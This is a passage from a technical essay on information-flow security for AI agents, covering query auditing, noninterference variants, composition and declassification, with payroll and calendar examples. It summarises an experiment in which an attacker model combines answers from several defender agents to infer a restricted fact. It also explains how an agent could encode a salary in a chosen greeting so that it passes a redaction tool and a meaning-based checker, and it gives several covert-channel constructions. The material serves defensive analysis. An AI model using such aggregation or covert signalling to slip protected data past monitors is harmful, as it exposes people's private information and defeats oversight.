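Suppose the agent has collected the totals without Eve (315), without Dee (320), without Cy (330) and without Bo (335). Subtracting neighboring totals shows that Eve earns 5 more than Dee, Dee 10 more than Cy, and Cy 5 more than Bo. The auditing program has protected each person's salary, as intended, but not the gaps between salaries, which the company might also want to keep private. Anyone who has these totals and knows one of the five salaries can calculate the other four, so Bo could do it after reading a report from the agent that contains the totals.

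Auditing can also be expensive. With enough kinds of question, working out whether a new answer would disclose something becomes computationally infeasible.

### Refusals that leak

When a program audits totals in this way, it can use the groups in the questions to determine whether a new answer would reveal an exact salary. It never needs to look at the pay data, so its refusals reveal nothing about pay. This isn't true for every kind of question.

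Suppose a tool reports the largest value in a group and has told an agent that max(a, b, c) = 9. The agent then asks for max(a, b). If the answer is 9, the tool can give it safely, because the agent still can't tell whether a or b is 9, or how large c is. If the answer is less than 9, giving it would reveal that c = 9, so the tool refuses. But the refusal is itself an output that depends on protected data, and an agent that knows the rule can infer from it that c = 9.

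*Simulatable auditing* (Kenthapadi, Mishra and Nissim, 2005) avoids the problem by having the program decide whether to answer using only the new question and the earlier questions and answers, without the true answer to the new question. In the simplest version, the program considers every set of values that fits the earlier answers, and refuses if the new answer would be revealing for any of them. The agent already has all the information used in this decision and could simulate it, so it learns nothing new from a refusal. According to *Query Auditing*, lecture slides from the University of Texas at Austin, simulatable auditors "provably don't leak information about actual data values".

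In the example, the first answer is consistent with a = 5, b = 7 and c = 9, and with those values max(a, b) would be revealing. The program therefore refuses to give max(a, b) whatever the data are, even when the answer is a harmless 9. This keeps its refusals from leaking anything, but it means the program refuses more often.

*Statistical Database Auditing Without Query Denial Threat* instead proposes that the auditing program derive everything each refusal reveals and count it along with the earlier answers when it audits the next question. This method works for mixtures of totals, maximums, minimums and some other statistics.

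### Facts split among several agents

Patil and colleagues tested something like query auditing, with language models in place of the auditing program. They built 119 scenarios in which several defender agents each hold one table and another agent, the attacker, questions them one at a time. No table is sensitive by itself, and the attacker can reach its target only by combining answers. In one scenario, the attacker has to find out who took a company-funded flight to Honolulu. It identifies Jane Smith in marketing by combining flights, payment methods, personal details and approvals. The scenarios also include harmless targets that require the same kind of combining, so a defender can't score well by refusing everything.

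None of the tables in these scenarios is a protected input, and none contains the sensitive fact the attacker is after. A noninterference test would have no protected input to vary, so every scenario would pass, including those in which the attacker learns the fact.

The attacker was always Qwen3-32B, an open-weights model. The defenders ran on Qwen3-32B, Gemini 2.5 Pro or GPT-5, with one of six defenses:

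- *Reasoning only*: the defender thinks step by step about its own table.
- *List*: the defender also has a list of sensitive combinations.
- *List and history*: the defender has the list and a record of past questions.
- *Theory of mind*: the defender has the list and history, and also estimates what the questioner already knows and could infer.
- *Self-voting*: the defender has the list and history, votes several times on whether to answer, and refuses if any vote is against.
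- *Collaboration*: the defenders pool their histories and all vote, and one vote against is enough to refuse.

In each cell below, the first number is the percentage of sensitive scenarios in which the attacker completely failed to infer the target, and the second is the percentage of benign scenarios in which it fully succeeded.

| Defense | Qwen3-32B | Gemini 2.5 Pro | GPT-5 |
|---|---|---|---|
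| Reasoning only | 31.1 / 68.9 | 34.1 / 65.9 | 70.5 / 63.6 |
| List | 35.8 / 76.4 | 33.7 / 67.3 | 75.9 / 64.4 |
| List and history | 29.8 / 64.4 | 39.1 / 73.9 | 92.1 / 64.0 |
| Theory of mind | 88.8 / 57.1 | 96.6 / 52.9 | 94.2 / 61.6 |
| Self-voting | 97.1 / 57.4 | 92.7 / 61.0 | 81.1 / 65.6 |
| Collaboration | 86.5 / 70.2 | 89.9 / 69.7 | 88.0 / 66.3 |

The top row is worse than it looks. With Qwen3-32B defending, the attacker failed in 31.1% of sensitive scenarios, but it also fell short in 31.1% of benign ones. Gemini's two failure rates match as well, at 34.1%. A sensitive scenario counts as blocked whenever the attacker fails, for whatever reason, so these are the results we would expect from defenders that made no distinction between harmful and harmless combinations. GPT-5 did distinguish them, with failure rates of 70.5% and 36.4%. (The paper's abstract gives a blocking rate of about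 39% for step-by-step reasoning alone, which matches none of the three models.)

Query auditing relies on a history of past questions. Adding this history to the list made Qwen3-32B slightly worse at blocking, while GPT-5 improved from 75.9% to 92.1%. The history therefore seems to help only if the model can work out what the past answers reveal together. Self-voting gave Qwen3-32B the same list and history and raised its blocking rate from 29.8% to 97.1%, which suggests that the model already had enough information but was using it badly.

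Blocking sensitive combinations while allowing benign ones remained difficult. Patil and colleagues paired each sensitive scenario with a benign one and counted the pairs in which the attacker failed in the sensitive scenario and succeeded in the benign one. The best result was 61.8% of pairs, for Gemini with collaboration.

In every scenario, the attacker also received a correct plan describing the steps that would lead to the target. Patil and colleagues supplied the plan to approximate an upper bound on leakage, since a scenario might otherwise seem safe only because the attacker never thought of the right questions. The results therefore don't estimate how often an agent would piece together a restricted fact in ordinary work, when it might not be looking for one. They also aren't a strict upper bound, because Qwen3-32B still had to word the questions, deal with refusals and draw the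 conclusion, all of which a stronger model might do better.

### Database remedies for agents

Surapani and colleagues argue that permitted accesses can add up to forbidden knowledge in both databases and agents, but that the database remedies of query auditing and adding noise to answers "do not translate directly" to agents. Their reason is that databases in this literature have fixed records and answer statistical questions, whereas an agent receives changing outputs of many kinds and combines them by reasoning in natural language. Tallam adds that the agent combines them using a neural network whose behavior nobody has formally specified, that it may find new sources as it works, and that whoever asked for the result may not know which sources contributed to it.

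The lack of a specification for the network matters least. An auditing program works out what follows from the answers, which is the same for a person, a spreadsheet or a language model, so it doesn't need to predict how the questioner will reason. If the payroll tool audits its totals, an agent can't deduce Eve's salary from those totals alone, however intelligent it is. For tools that answer structured questions about a table, auditing works for agents without changes.

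Changing data are difficult to handle, and Denning and colleagues excluded them by assuming that nobody updates the database during an attack. Suppose the department total is 410 on Monday and 417 on Friday, and the agent has read a notice that only Eve got a raise that week. The agent can infer that her raise was 7. An auditing program that treated Friday's question as a repeat of Monday's would miss this inference. To catch it, the program would have to treat Eve's old and new salaries as separate unknowns and protect the raise as well.

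A bigger difficulty arises when the agent has several tools. Suppose the payroll tool audits its own answers perfectly, but the agent also has a budget tool that reports each department's wage bill. The payroll tool gives the total for everyone in Eve's department except her, which exposes nobody according to its own records. The budget tool gives the total for the whole department, 410. Neither tool has a record of the other's answers, so neither detects that the agent can subtract one total from the other to get Eve's salary. The company could fix this by using a single auditing program for both tools, as long as the outputs are numbers with known meanings.

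Surapani and colleagues are right about emails, tickets and calendars. An auditing program needs a set of possibilities to check, such as all the lists of salaries that fit the answers so far. Nobody can list every situation that fits the contents of an inbox, and a simulatable auditor would also have to consider every reply that the next search might return. Adding noise doesn't help much either. A salary total that is off by 3 may still be accurate enough for planning a budget, but an agent needs the exact date to book a flight.

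Such data can only be protected by judgment, like that of the defenders in the experiment by Patil and colleagues, and that protection comes without a proof. Those defenders also see their own tables when they decide whether to answer, so their refusals could leak information in the same way as the refusal to give max(a, b).

Lahjouji and Colaco recommend information-flow control, which labels data and carries the labels along when programs combine the data. In their survey, it is the only mechanism that covers both leaks from combining sources and inference across sessions. *Secure Databases* (1979) rejected an early form of this idea for databases, arguing that mechanisms that track where information came from don't interpret its content or record what they have already released.

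The payroll tool shows the limits of each position. If every total keeps a high label, the system can withhold them all, and the agent has nothing to subtract. But if the company approves totals covering four or more people as low, the agent can get all six and calculate Eve's salary from them. In the pharmacy, names and purchases are low from the start, so labels would help only if somebody wrote a rule against combining them.

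Tallam considers the aggregation problem unsolved in general and suggests limiting which sources an agent may combine and tracking which results each output depends on. Tallam cites a monitor called PCAS that does such tracking and raised compliance with stated policies from 48% to 93%. This is good evidence that a system can enforce a rule about combinations, but someone has to identify a dangerous combination before they can write a rule against it.

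## Agents that act at random, adapt and reuse their own outputs

The proofs so far assumed deterministic machines, but language models are rarely run deterministically. At each step, the model computes a probability for every possible next word, and the program running it usually picks one at random according to those probabilities. The same prompt can therefore produce different replies.

Suppose a law firm's reception agent can read the lawyers' calendar, which is high, and answers questions from visitors, who are the low observers. A visitor asks when the office opens. The agent writes "We open at nine" in one run and "Nine o'clock" in another. If the first reply followed a history in which a lawyer booked a meeting, and the second followed the purged history, Goguen and Meseguer's equation fails, as if the agent had leaked something about the meeting. But the replies can differ by chance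 just as easily when nobody has booked anything, so it makes no sense to require single outputs from two runs to be equal.

Brackin, Foley and colleagues (1996), in *Romulus, a Computer Security Properties Modeling Environment*, describe the 1982 condition as meaningful only for deterministic systems. Ryan and Schneider, in *Process Algebra and Non-interference*, explain that the equation is straightforward when each history determines the low output, but that otherwise someone has to define "equal". Computer scientists have several competing definitions of when two systems behave equivalently, and Ryan and Schneider suspect that none is right for every purpose.

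If an observing agent's tools are deterministic and satisfy noninterference, making random choices doesn't help it infer what the high users do. Suppose the program draws all its random numbers before the run starts. For any particular list of numbers the agent is deterministic, so by the earlier proof about chained calls, its view is the same whatever the high users do. This holds for every list, and the lists don't depend on protected data, so the probability of each view is the same too. Problems arise when the component that makes random choices also handles protected data, as the reception agent does.

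### Comparing what is possible

One repair is to compare sets of possible outputs. Von Oheimb's *Information Flow Control Revisited* requires every output possible after one history to be possible after any other history that purges to the same sequence. The comparison has to run in both directions. Suppose a tool replies 0 or 1 at random if the lawyer has filed nothing, and always replies 0 if the lawyer has filed a memo. Every reply possible with a memo is also possible without one, so a check in that direction alone would pass, but an agent that receives 1 knows there is no memo.

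Daryl McCullough's *generalized noninterference*, from the late 1980s, applies the same idea to whole runs. McLean (1994), in *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets Closed Under Selective Interleaving*, states it roughly as follows. Take any two possible runs. There must be a third possible run that has the high inputs of one and the low inputs and low outputs of the other. The high outputs of this third run can be anything. (McCullough's original is slightly stronger, because it lets high outputs change only after the point where the high inputs change.)

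The reception agent's answer about opening hours meets the condition. In one run, a meeting is booked and the agent replies "Nine o'clock". In another, no meeting is booked and it replies "We open at nine". The condition requires that a run with the meeting and the reply "We open at nine" also be possible. It is, because the agent could have used either phrase whether or not a meeting was booked.

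But the condition also passes tools that leak badly. O'Neill, Clarkson and Chong, in *Information-Flow Security for Interactive Programs*, give the example of a program that reads a secret number. If the number is even, the program outputs 0 with probability 0.99 and 1 with probability 0.01. If the number is odd, the probabilities are reversed. The program passes because both outputs are possible in both cases. Yet an observer who initially thought even and odd equally likely should be 99% sure that the number is even after seeing a 0. An agent that calls the tool three times, with a fresh random choice each time, and goes with the majority will be wrong only about 3 times in 10,000.

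This flaw makes the condition nearly worthless for language models. Unless the developer cuts off unlikely words, a model gives every word a nonzero probability, so any text is a possible reply to any prompt. An HR agent that reads the payroll table and tells everyone who asks that Dee earns 90 would meet the condition, because there is a tiny chance it would have written the same thing if Dee earned 70.

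A system can also lose the property when a developer makes it less random. In McLean's example, a system starts out able to produce every combination of high and low behavior. If the developer keeps only the runs in which the system repeats each high input as a low output one step later, the system no longer has the property, even though the developer has added no new behavior. Setting a language model's temperature, which controls its randomness, to zero also removes many possible replies, because the model then always picks the likeliest word. A certificate based on possible outputs at one temperature therefore may not hold at another.

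### A user who reacts

Todd Wittbold and Dale Johnson found a different problem in 1990. Their example, which O'Neill and colleagues rewrote as a short program, is a system that works in rounds. In each round, the system picks a random bit x and shows it to High, who replies with a bit y. The system then shows Low the value x XOR y, which is 0 if the bits are the same and 1 if they differ.

| High sees x | High sends y | Low sees x XOR y |
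|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 0 | 1 | 1 |
| 1 | 0 | 1 |
| 1 | 1 | 0 |

High could have sent either 0 or 1, whichever bit Low sees. Low can't rule out any input, however many rounds go by, so the system satisfies nondeducibility for High's inputs. It also satisfies generalized noninterference.

High can still send Low any message. To send a bit z, High waits to see x and then replies with y = z XOR x. Low sees x XOR z XOR x, which equals z because the two x's cancel. For example, if High wants to send 1, 0, 1 and the system shows High 0, 1, 1, High replies with 1, 1, 0 and Low sees 1, 0, 1. As O'Neill and colleagues point out, the system never receives z, either as an input or as a starting value. Protecting the inputs is therefore not enough, because the secret is in how High chooses them.

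This program is unsafe because of the order of its instructions. *Non-Interference for Deterministic Interactive Programs* (Clark and Hunt, 2008) compares it with a program that has the same instructions but takes y before it shows High x. The second program is safe because High has to choose y without knowing x, so Low sees a random bit whatever High does.

To tell them apart, Wittbold and Johnson considered High's strategy, a rule that determines High's next input from everything High has seen and sent so far. A system satisfies *nondeducibility on strategies* if the set of Low's possible views is the same whatever strategy High follows. The XOR system fails because Low sees only 0s if High always replies with y = x, and only 1s if High always replies with the opposite of x. The safe program passes, but so does O'Neill and colleagues' tool with probabilities of 0.99 and 0.01, because this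 condition still depends only on which views are possible.

High can leak information without intending to. Clark and Hunt, who credit the example to David Sands, describe a website that asks Alice for her credit card number (simplified to a single bit) and gives her a discount code to enter later. The code is her card number XORed with a random bit that the site keeps. When Alice enters the code, the site XORs it with the same bit, recovers her card number and sends it to Bob. The site would fail the ordinary test if it sent the number to Bob directly. This version passes because Alice might have typed something other than the code, so whatever Bob sees is compatible with any card number.

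This would probably work on an agent shopping on Alice's behalf, because agents constantly copy confirmation codes, session numbers and file names from one tool result into the next call. An agent that picks each call after seeing the last result is following a strategy, which the tool's developer can often predict. If developers check a tool that behaves randomly against only fixed lists of inputs, they miss the way an agent will use it.

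### Why deterministic systems escape

Clark and Hunt proved that fixed lists are enough if the system is deterministic. Their intuition is that a High user could in principle predict all of a deterministic system's outputs, and so gains nothing by waiting to see them.

The proof replays a run. High first follows some strategy while Low behaves in a fixed way, and we record the inputs High sends. We then run the system again, with High sending the same inputs without looking at any replies. A deterministic system repeats the same run, so Low sees the same thing. If two strategies give Low different views, the two recorded lists will too, and the ordinary test will catch the leak. For example, if the XOR system always used x = 0, Low would see y and the system would fail the test. With a random x, the system passes the test even though High can still leak information to Low.

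The theorem requires the system to be deterministic, but its users can act at random. The theorem therefore covers an agent that samples its words, as long as the agent is a user of the system and not part of it.

According to *A Comparison of Semantic Models for Noninterference* (van der Meyden and Zhang, 2008), strategies also make no difference in asynchronous systems, where High can take any amount of time to act. In the paper's model, a system satisfies nondeducibility on inputs only if everything Low might see is also possible when High has done nothing. The set of possible Low views is then the same for every strategy, because High might follow it too slowly to affect anything before Low looks. The XOR system already fails nondeducibility on inputs in this setting, because Low receives a bit only after High has sent one and so learns that High has acted.

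This result offers little protection in practice. Suppose the XOR system were changed to show Low a random bit whenever High was late. It could then pass the test, because High might always be late. But an agent that nearly always replies in time could still send almost any message.

### Comparing probabilities

*Probabilistic noninterference*, which James Gray introduced in 1991, requires the probabilities of Low's views to be the same, not just the set of possible views. Gray (1992) developed a general model of probabilistic computer systems and gave two definitions of secure information flow in it. The version by O'Neill and colleagues is easy to state. Let P(v | h, l) be the probability that Low sees v when High follows strategy h and Low follows strategy l. The system is secure if

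P(v | h, l) = P(v | h′, l)

for every view v, every Low strategy l and every pair of High strategies h and h′. To calculate one of these probabilities, we multiply the probabilities of the random choices along a run, then add up the results for all the runs that give Low the view v.

This condition correctly rejects both of the problematic examples. The program that reads a secret number outputs 0 with probability 0.99 if High enters an even number and 0.01 if High enters an odd one, so it fails. In the XOR system, where x is a fair coin toss, High can choose a strategy that makes the probability that Low sees a 1 either 0 or 1, so that system also fails. If the system no longer shows x to High, that probability is one half whatever High does, and the system passes.

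O'Neill and colleagues add that a low user can't form more accurate beliefs about High's behavior by interacting with a system that meets the condition. The condition also agrees with other work. In *A Logical Approach to Multilevel Security of Probabilistic Systems*, Gray and Syverson built a logic that expresses time, probability and knowledge, and showed that two definitions of perfect security in that logic were equivalent to earlier ones. Clark and Hunt cite Jan Jürjens's proof that Gray's condition generalizes nondeducibility on strategies.

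Its weakness is that it rejects systems over differences too small to matter. Suppose the safe XOR program used a slightly biased coin, so that x was 1 with probability 0.51. Low would see a 1 with probability 0.51 if High sent 0 and 0.49 if High sent 1. The program would fail the test, although Low could learn almost nothing about High's input from a single output bit.

Language models constantly have this problem because almost any change to a prompt changes the next word's probabilities at least slightly. If the calendar has one more meeting in it, the reception agent's probability of writing "Nine o'clock" might go from 0.400000 to 0.400001. No visitor could detect this change, but it violates the equation. So an agent that reads protected data and then writes to an observer will pass the tests of possibility almost regardless of what it does, and will almost always fail the exact test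 of probability. Developers also can't read the probabilities directly from a whole agent, so they have to estimate them from repeated runs.

### Secure parts, insecure whole

McCullough showed that a combined system can fail the condition even when every part satisfies it, so developers can't safely check each tool once and then combine tools freely. Brackin, McCullough and colleagues give an example with two systems that exchange high messages. We can think of the systems as two assistants, A and B, working for a client.

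Each assistant can receive private messages from the client and exchange private messages with the other assistant. Either may also send extra private messages at any time as padding. At some point A announces "stop", which ends the private messages. Each assistant then publishes "odd" or "even", depending on how many private messages it has sent and received.

An observer who sees only A's word can't rule out any particular number of client messages, because A might have sent one more padding message and turned "odd" into "even". The same is true of B, so both assistants satisfy nondeducibility for the client's messages.

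Suppose the assistants exchange d messages with each other and the client sends n messages to A. A's count is n + d and B's is d, so the assistants publish the same word if n is even and different words if n is odd. An observer who compares the two words therefore learns whether n is odd or even. The padding hid n in A's report, but B counted the same padding, so it cancels out, much as x does in the XOR system.

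McLean added probabilities to another of McCullough's examples to examine whether the parts in such examples were already leaking a little in ways that tests of possibility missed. In this example, a planner receives private jobs from outside and sends each one to a worker, which sends it back. When the planner is told to cancel, it forwards the instruction to the worker. Each of them may then post a public notice that it had nothing to cancel, but only if it had no job in hand.

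Suppose each posts the notice half the time when it has no job in hand, and that each, when running on its own, works so fast that it has always passed on its last job before the instruction to cancel arrives. Each then posts the notice with probability one half whatever the high users do, so neither leaks anything, even in probability.

Once they are connected, a job that enters the loop never leaves it. If messages travel instantly, either the planner or the worker always has the job, so they can't both post the notice. These are McLean's probabilities for what an observer sees:

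| Public notices | No private job | A private job |
|---|---|---|
| Neither posts | 25% | 50% |
| Only the planner posts | 25% | 25% |
| Only the worker posts | 25% | 25% |
| Both post | 25% | 0% |

Connecting the two parts creates a leak, though neither part had one. McLean calculates that a malicious high program could use this leak to send about 0.17 bits each time, or one bit in roughly six uses.

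### What survives being connected

McLean separates three ways of connecting systems. In a product, the systems run side by side. In a cascade, the outputs of one become the inputs of the other. In feedback, the second system's outputs also return to the first. Generalized noninterference still holds after systems are connected by product or cascade, but not always with feedback. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995) proved a conjecture of McCullough's that noninterference is preserved when systems are composed without feedback, and gave a way to compose systems with feedback that also preserves it.

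McLean's explanation is that feedback eliminates runs. Tests of possibility require certain runs to exist, such as one that combines the high inputs of one run with the low outputs of another. In a cascade, the worker only has to accept what the planner sends. With feedback, the planner must also accept what the worker sends back at every step, so a run that each could have produced separately may no longer be possible.

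McCullough's solution was a stronger condition, *restrictiveness*, which he presents in McCullough (1990), in *A hookup theorem for multilevel security*. Like the unwinding theorem, it uses a relation between states that look alike to Low. A machine is restrictive if some such relation meets three requirements:

- The machine accepts every input in every state.
- If two states look alike and the machine receives the same low inputs in both, it can reach states that still look alike, whatever high inputs came with them.
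- If the machine can produce some outputs from one state, then from any state that looks like it, the machine can produce outputs that are the same for Low and reach a state that again looks alike.

Assistant B fails. A private message can change its count from even to odd, and the states before and after the message have to look alike, even once "stop" arrives. But B can't send any more padding by then, so it has to publish "even" in one state and "odd" in the other. A avoids this problem because it decides when to stop and can send a padding message first. We could repair B by letting it send one more private message after "stop", too late for A to count. The words A and B publish could then differ even if the client had sent nothing.

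Any combination of restrictive machines is restrictive, including combinations with feedback. But restrictiveness depends only on which behaviors are possible, not on how likely they are, so the tool with probabilities of 0.99 and 0.01 can satisfy it.

McLean proposed a simpler condition, *separability*, which is also preserved under feedback. A system is separable if everything High sends and sees in one run can occur together with everything Low sends and sees in any other run. The high and low halves are in effect independent, which rules out any system in which low events affect high ones, such as one that records visitors' questions in an audit file for the lawyers.

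### Agents that read what they wrote

Agents have a great deal of feedback, meaning that what they produce affects what they receive. They save notes and read them later, write files and open them again, and send other agents questions and receive their replies.

Some feedback is easy to miss. A search agent that passes its results to a summarizing agent forms a cascade with it only if the summarizing agent sends nothing back, not even a question or "queue full". Mardziel (2007) describes a variation on McCullough's example in which two low programs each fill a one-bit buffer and then have to wait. A high program reads a secret bit and empties one of the buffers, depending on the bit. The low program that can now continue publishes its own number, 0 or 1, which reveals the secret. Mardziel doubts that this is really a case of secure parts forming an insecure whole, because the high program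 influences a low one by emptying its buffer, so information travels against the arrow in the diagram. A check of agents therefore has to treat a queue with limited space as a connection in both directions.

A check must also cover what the agent saves between runs. Suppose an agent XORs a secret bit with a random bit, publishes the result on Monday and saves the random bit in its notes. On Tuesday it reads the notes and publishes the random bit as a reference number. Each published bit is random by itself, but together they reveal the secret. A check of Monday's run that ignored the notes would find nothing wrong. If the check treats the notes as low, Monday's run fails, because the notes and the published bit together depend on the secret. If it treats them as high, Tuesday's run fails, because the published reference number depends on high data.

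Checking each tool separately is enough if every tool is deterministic and satisfies noninterference for the observer. For the deterministic machines that Goguen and Meseguer considered, restrictiveness and noninterference are the same condition, so the tools remain secure when a developer connects them, with or without feedback. They also remain secure when an agent uses them as a low user, even if it samples its words, adapts to each result and keeps notes. The payroll and budget tools that jointly revealed Eve's salary each failed noninterference, so they are consistent with this result.

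Separate checks can also work for random tools whose random choices do not depend on protected data. Suppose each tool draws all its random numbers before the run, so that it is deterministic for any particular draw. If every tool satisfies noninterference for every draw, the developer can combine them safely, and the probability of each view will not depend on what High does. A tool that picks a greeting at random passes this check. The tool with probabilities of 0.99 and 0.01 fails if it works in the usual way, drawing a number between 0 and 1 and outputting 0 when the number is below the relevant probability. A draw of 0.5 then produces 0 for an even secret and 1 for an odd one.

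This check is stricter than necessary. O'Neill and colleagues use a similar technique for choices with unknown probabilities, and Clark and Hunt object that the resulting condition rejects the safe XOR program as well as the unsafe one.

Each tool also needs its own random numbers. O'Neill and colleagues show that a program can leak a secret when high and low choices use the same list of random numbers. Suppose the next two entries are 1 and 0. A program reads a secret bit, and if the bit is 0, it makes a random choice that has no effect but uses up the 1. It then publishes the next entry, which equals the secret bit. Developers risk creating this leak when they give all their agents' components one fixed list of random numbers so that they can reproduce a run exactly.

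An agent that reads protected data and writes to low observers will almost never pass such a check, so checking its tools doesn't establish whether the whole system is secure. Brackin and colleagues suggest avoiding this problem by giving each untrusted program a level and applying Bell and LaPadula's two rules, treating what it receives as reading and what it sends as writing. The program then can't break the system's security however it behaves, as long as every other part is either restrictive or confined in the same way. A language model confined like this doesn't need to be analyzed, even if it samples, adapts or follows an attacker's instructions.

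The law firm could use two agents. One would read the calendar and write only to the lawyers, and the other would answer visitors without access to the calendar. That works for questions about opening hours but not for booking appointments, because visitors can't find out which times are free unless some information from the calendar reaches them.

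## Conditions that allow some disclosure

An agent that offers a visitor even one appointment time fails noninterference, and so does a tool that gives a manager the department's total pay. Most useful agents have to release some information like this. Computer scientists have relaxed noninterference mainly by restricting the route that protected data may take, listing which information may be released, or limiting how much may be released.

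### Release through an intermediary

Rushby uses the example of a device that encrypts messages before they reach a network. A component called Red receives each message and sends its body through an encryption unit, Crypto. Red sends the header unencrypted through a unit called Bypass, because the network's switches have to read it. A component called Black reassembles the two parts and sends them out. The policy has four arrows: Red → Crypto, Red → Bypass, Crypto → Black and Bypass → Black.

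The policy has no arrow from Red to Black, so it is intransitive, and the ordinary condition can't express it. With Red ↛ Black, purging a history for Black deletes everything Red did, so the device fails the condition as soon as Black sends out one of Red's messages. Adding the arrow Red → Black would allow Red to pass plaintext straight to the network. Goguen and Meseguer suggested a solution in 1982, but Rushby says it was incorrect and credits Haigh and Young with the first satisfactory treatment a few years later.

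Haigh and Young's condition, *intransitive noninterference*, deletes an action only if no permitted chain of later actions could have carried its effects to the observer. In Rushby's notation, sources(α, u) is the set of domains that could affect u through such a chain in the sequence α:

- If α is empty, sources(α, u) contains only u.
- If α is an action a followed by a sequence β, take sources(β, u), and add dom(a) if dom(a) → v for some v already in that set.

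The new purge function, ipurge, goes through the sequence from the front. It keeps an action a, followed by β, if dom(a) is in sources(aβ, u), and otherwise drops it. The security condition is the same as before with ipurge in place of purge:

test(α, a) = test(ipurge(α, dom(a)), a)

Suppose a company's agent, A, reads personnel files and may send text out only through a redaction tool, R, which removes names and salaries. W is a reader outside the company. The policy is A → R, R → W, and A ↛ W.

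| Action, in order | Chain to W | Result |
|---|---|---|
| A submits a first draft | A → R → W | keep |
| R redacts the draft and sends it | R → W | keep |
| A submits a second draft | none, since R doesn't run again | delete |

W must see the same thing when it opens its inbox, with or without the second draft. The first draft may affect what W sees because R ran after it. The ordinary purge would have deleted both drafts.

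The unwinding theorem needs only one change, the weaker form of step consistency that some verified systems use. If two states look alike to both u and dom(a), they must still look alike to u after action a. What W sees after R runs may therefore depend on the draft, because R can see the draft. For systems made of storage locations, Rushby shows that an arrow from u to v is enough whenever u can write to a location that v can read, assuming the access table is accurate. The company has to find and close every other route from the agent to the outside, including search queries and shared folders. Such proofs are possible for real code. According to *Verifying Type Soundness for Nontransitive Information Flow Security* (2026), the seL4 proof establishes a variant of intransitive noninterference.

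### What the intermediary lets through

The condition doesn't limit what R sends. Rushby calls specifying what Crypto and Bypass must do "a separate problem". The policy would still hold if Red copied the body of a message into its header, or if a redaction tool forwarded every draft unchanged.

A redaction tool that works as intended can still leak information if the agent chooses the text. An agent following an attacker's instructions could open its message with "Dear colleague" if Dee earns more than 80 and with "Hello" if she doesn't. Neither greeting contains anything the tool is meant to remove. The company therefore has to specify the tool's behavior separately from the arrows, and the tool has to be safe for every draft the agent might write.

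Agent systems rely on the same assumption. *Agenra* (2026), an authorization system, assumes the agent may deliberately propose forbidden calls, but its scanners and trusted transformations "must do what they claim". *APPA* (2026) also treats the model as untrusted, but its formal guarantee does not cover faulty external tools. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), the intermediary is a separate language model call that receives only the protected records and the proposed output. It approves the output only if the output's meaning is unrelated to the records. This check might catch a paraphrased salary, but it would probably approve the coded message, because a greeting is unrelated in meaning to anyone's pay.

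In *Architectural Refinement and Notions of Intransitive Noninterference*, van der Meyden (2012) argues that Haigh and Young's definition permits flows that intransitive policies are meant to prevent. Suppose two agents each have their own redaction tool, and neither tool receives anything from the other agent. After both tools have run, the system shows an outside reader which agent submitted its draft first. The definition allows this because ipurge keeps both submissions in their original order. But neither tool had information about that order, so neither could have approved its release.

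Under TA-security, one of van der Meyden's replacements, a domain can pass on only information that the policy permitted it to have, which rules this example out. But a system can still satisfy TA-security when an intermediary forwards an email attachment without opening it. A stricter definition, based on what the intermediary has observed, is meant to exclude that case.

### Approved releases

*Declassification* is the deliberate release of some protected information under a policy. Sabelfeld and Myers, in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, define a condition for programs called *delimited release*. Its policy is a list of expressions e₁, …, eₙ whose values the observer may learn, such as the average of five salaries. Let M₁ and M₂ be any two possible starting memories, low(M) the part of memory M that the observer may see, and c(M) the memory after program c has run. The program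 satisfies delimited release if

low(M₁) = low(M₂) and eᵢ(M₁) = eᵢ(M₂) for every i ⟹ low(c(M₁)) = low(c(M₂))

One condition that allows some disclosure applies to a pair of runs only if every value approved for disclosure is the same in both. The observer must then see the same result in both runs. If no values are approved, the condition is ordinary noninterference.

Suppose the policy approves the average of the five salaries, which is 82. A program that outputs the average passes. Another program first overwrites all five salaries with Eve's and then outputs their average, 95. Checking only the line that releases the average would not catch this. But if we swap Dee's and Eve's salaries at the start, the approved average is still 82 while the output changes from 95 to 90, so the program fails. Sabelfeld and Myers call this a laundering attack, because the program uses an approved release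 to reveal something else.

Another example is an electronic wallet. A shop's program may test whether the balance is at least the price of an item and, if so, subtract the price. An attacker puts this test in a loop, with prices of 8, 4, 2 and 1. If the balance is 13, the first two tests succeed and leave 1, the third fails and the fourth succeeds, so the balance was 8 + 4 + 1 = 13. Each test has the approved form, but delimited release rejects the loop because the policy covers only one comparison between the starting balance and the starting price, and the loop reveals the whole balance.

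### Judging the whole list

Delimited release takes the list of approved disclosures as given, so it also permits a tool to reveal anything that can be worked out from them. Suppose a company approves both the department's payroll total, 410, and the total without Eve, 315. The condition compares only payroll tables that agree on both totals. Eve's salary is the difference between the totals, so it is the same in all of these tables, and a tool that prints "Eve earns 95" satisfies the condition.

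The HR company in effect approved the release of all six totals that its tool will give out. Any two payroll tables with the same six totals are identical, so a tool that prints the whole table would pass the test too. The calendar policy of Pandey and colleagues also exempts what the owner agreed to release, and they prove that some exemptions make such a condition trivial, meaning that every system satisfies it.

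Sabelfeld and Sands explain in *Declassification* that an approved expression determines only which secrets must look alike to the observer. Approving a value therefore has the same effect as approving any reversible transformation of it. If a policy approves the encrypted form of Eve's salary, and different salaries have different encrypted forms, the condition also accepts a program that publishes the salary unencrypted. The model does not account for how hard the encryption is to break.

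A reviewer should therefore judge the list by everything it implies. For each restricted fact, the reviewer checks whether some other possible table has the same approved values but makes the fact false. "Eve earns 95" passes if only the department total is approved, because tables with a different salary for Eve can also add up to 410, but it fails if both totals are approved. As with nondeducibility, the reviewer has to repeat this check for every possible table, not only the current one.

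Sabelfeld and Myers acknowledge that their condition treats everything on the list as released. It can't express "either the department total or the total without Eve, but not both", though they suggest adding policies of that kind. This limitation matters for an agent that chooses its own queries, because the company has to assume the agent will eventually collect every approved value.

Tools that take an argument are especially risky. Sabelfeld and Sands consider a function that tests whether a secret equals a value supplied by the user. Suitably chosen values can reveal the whole secret, so approving the function for all values amounts to approving the release of the secret. The same applies to a tool that reports whether Eve earns more than x, for any x the agent chooses. Approving only x = 80 would release much less.

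### Who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands classify declassification policies by four dimensions:

| Dimension | What the policy controls | Example for payroll |
|---|---|---|
| What | the information released | only the department total |
| Who | who controls the release | payroll staff choose the group |
| Where | the part of the system that releases it | only the reporting tool sends totals out |
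| When | the time or speed of release | only after the annual review |

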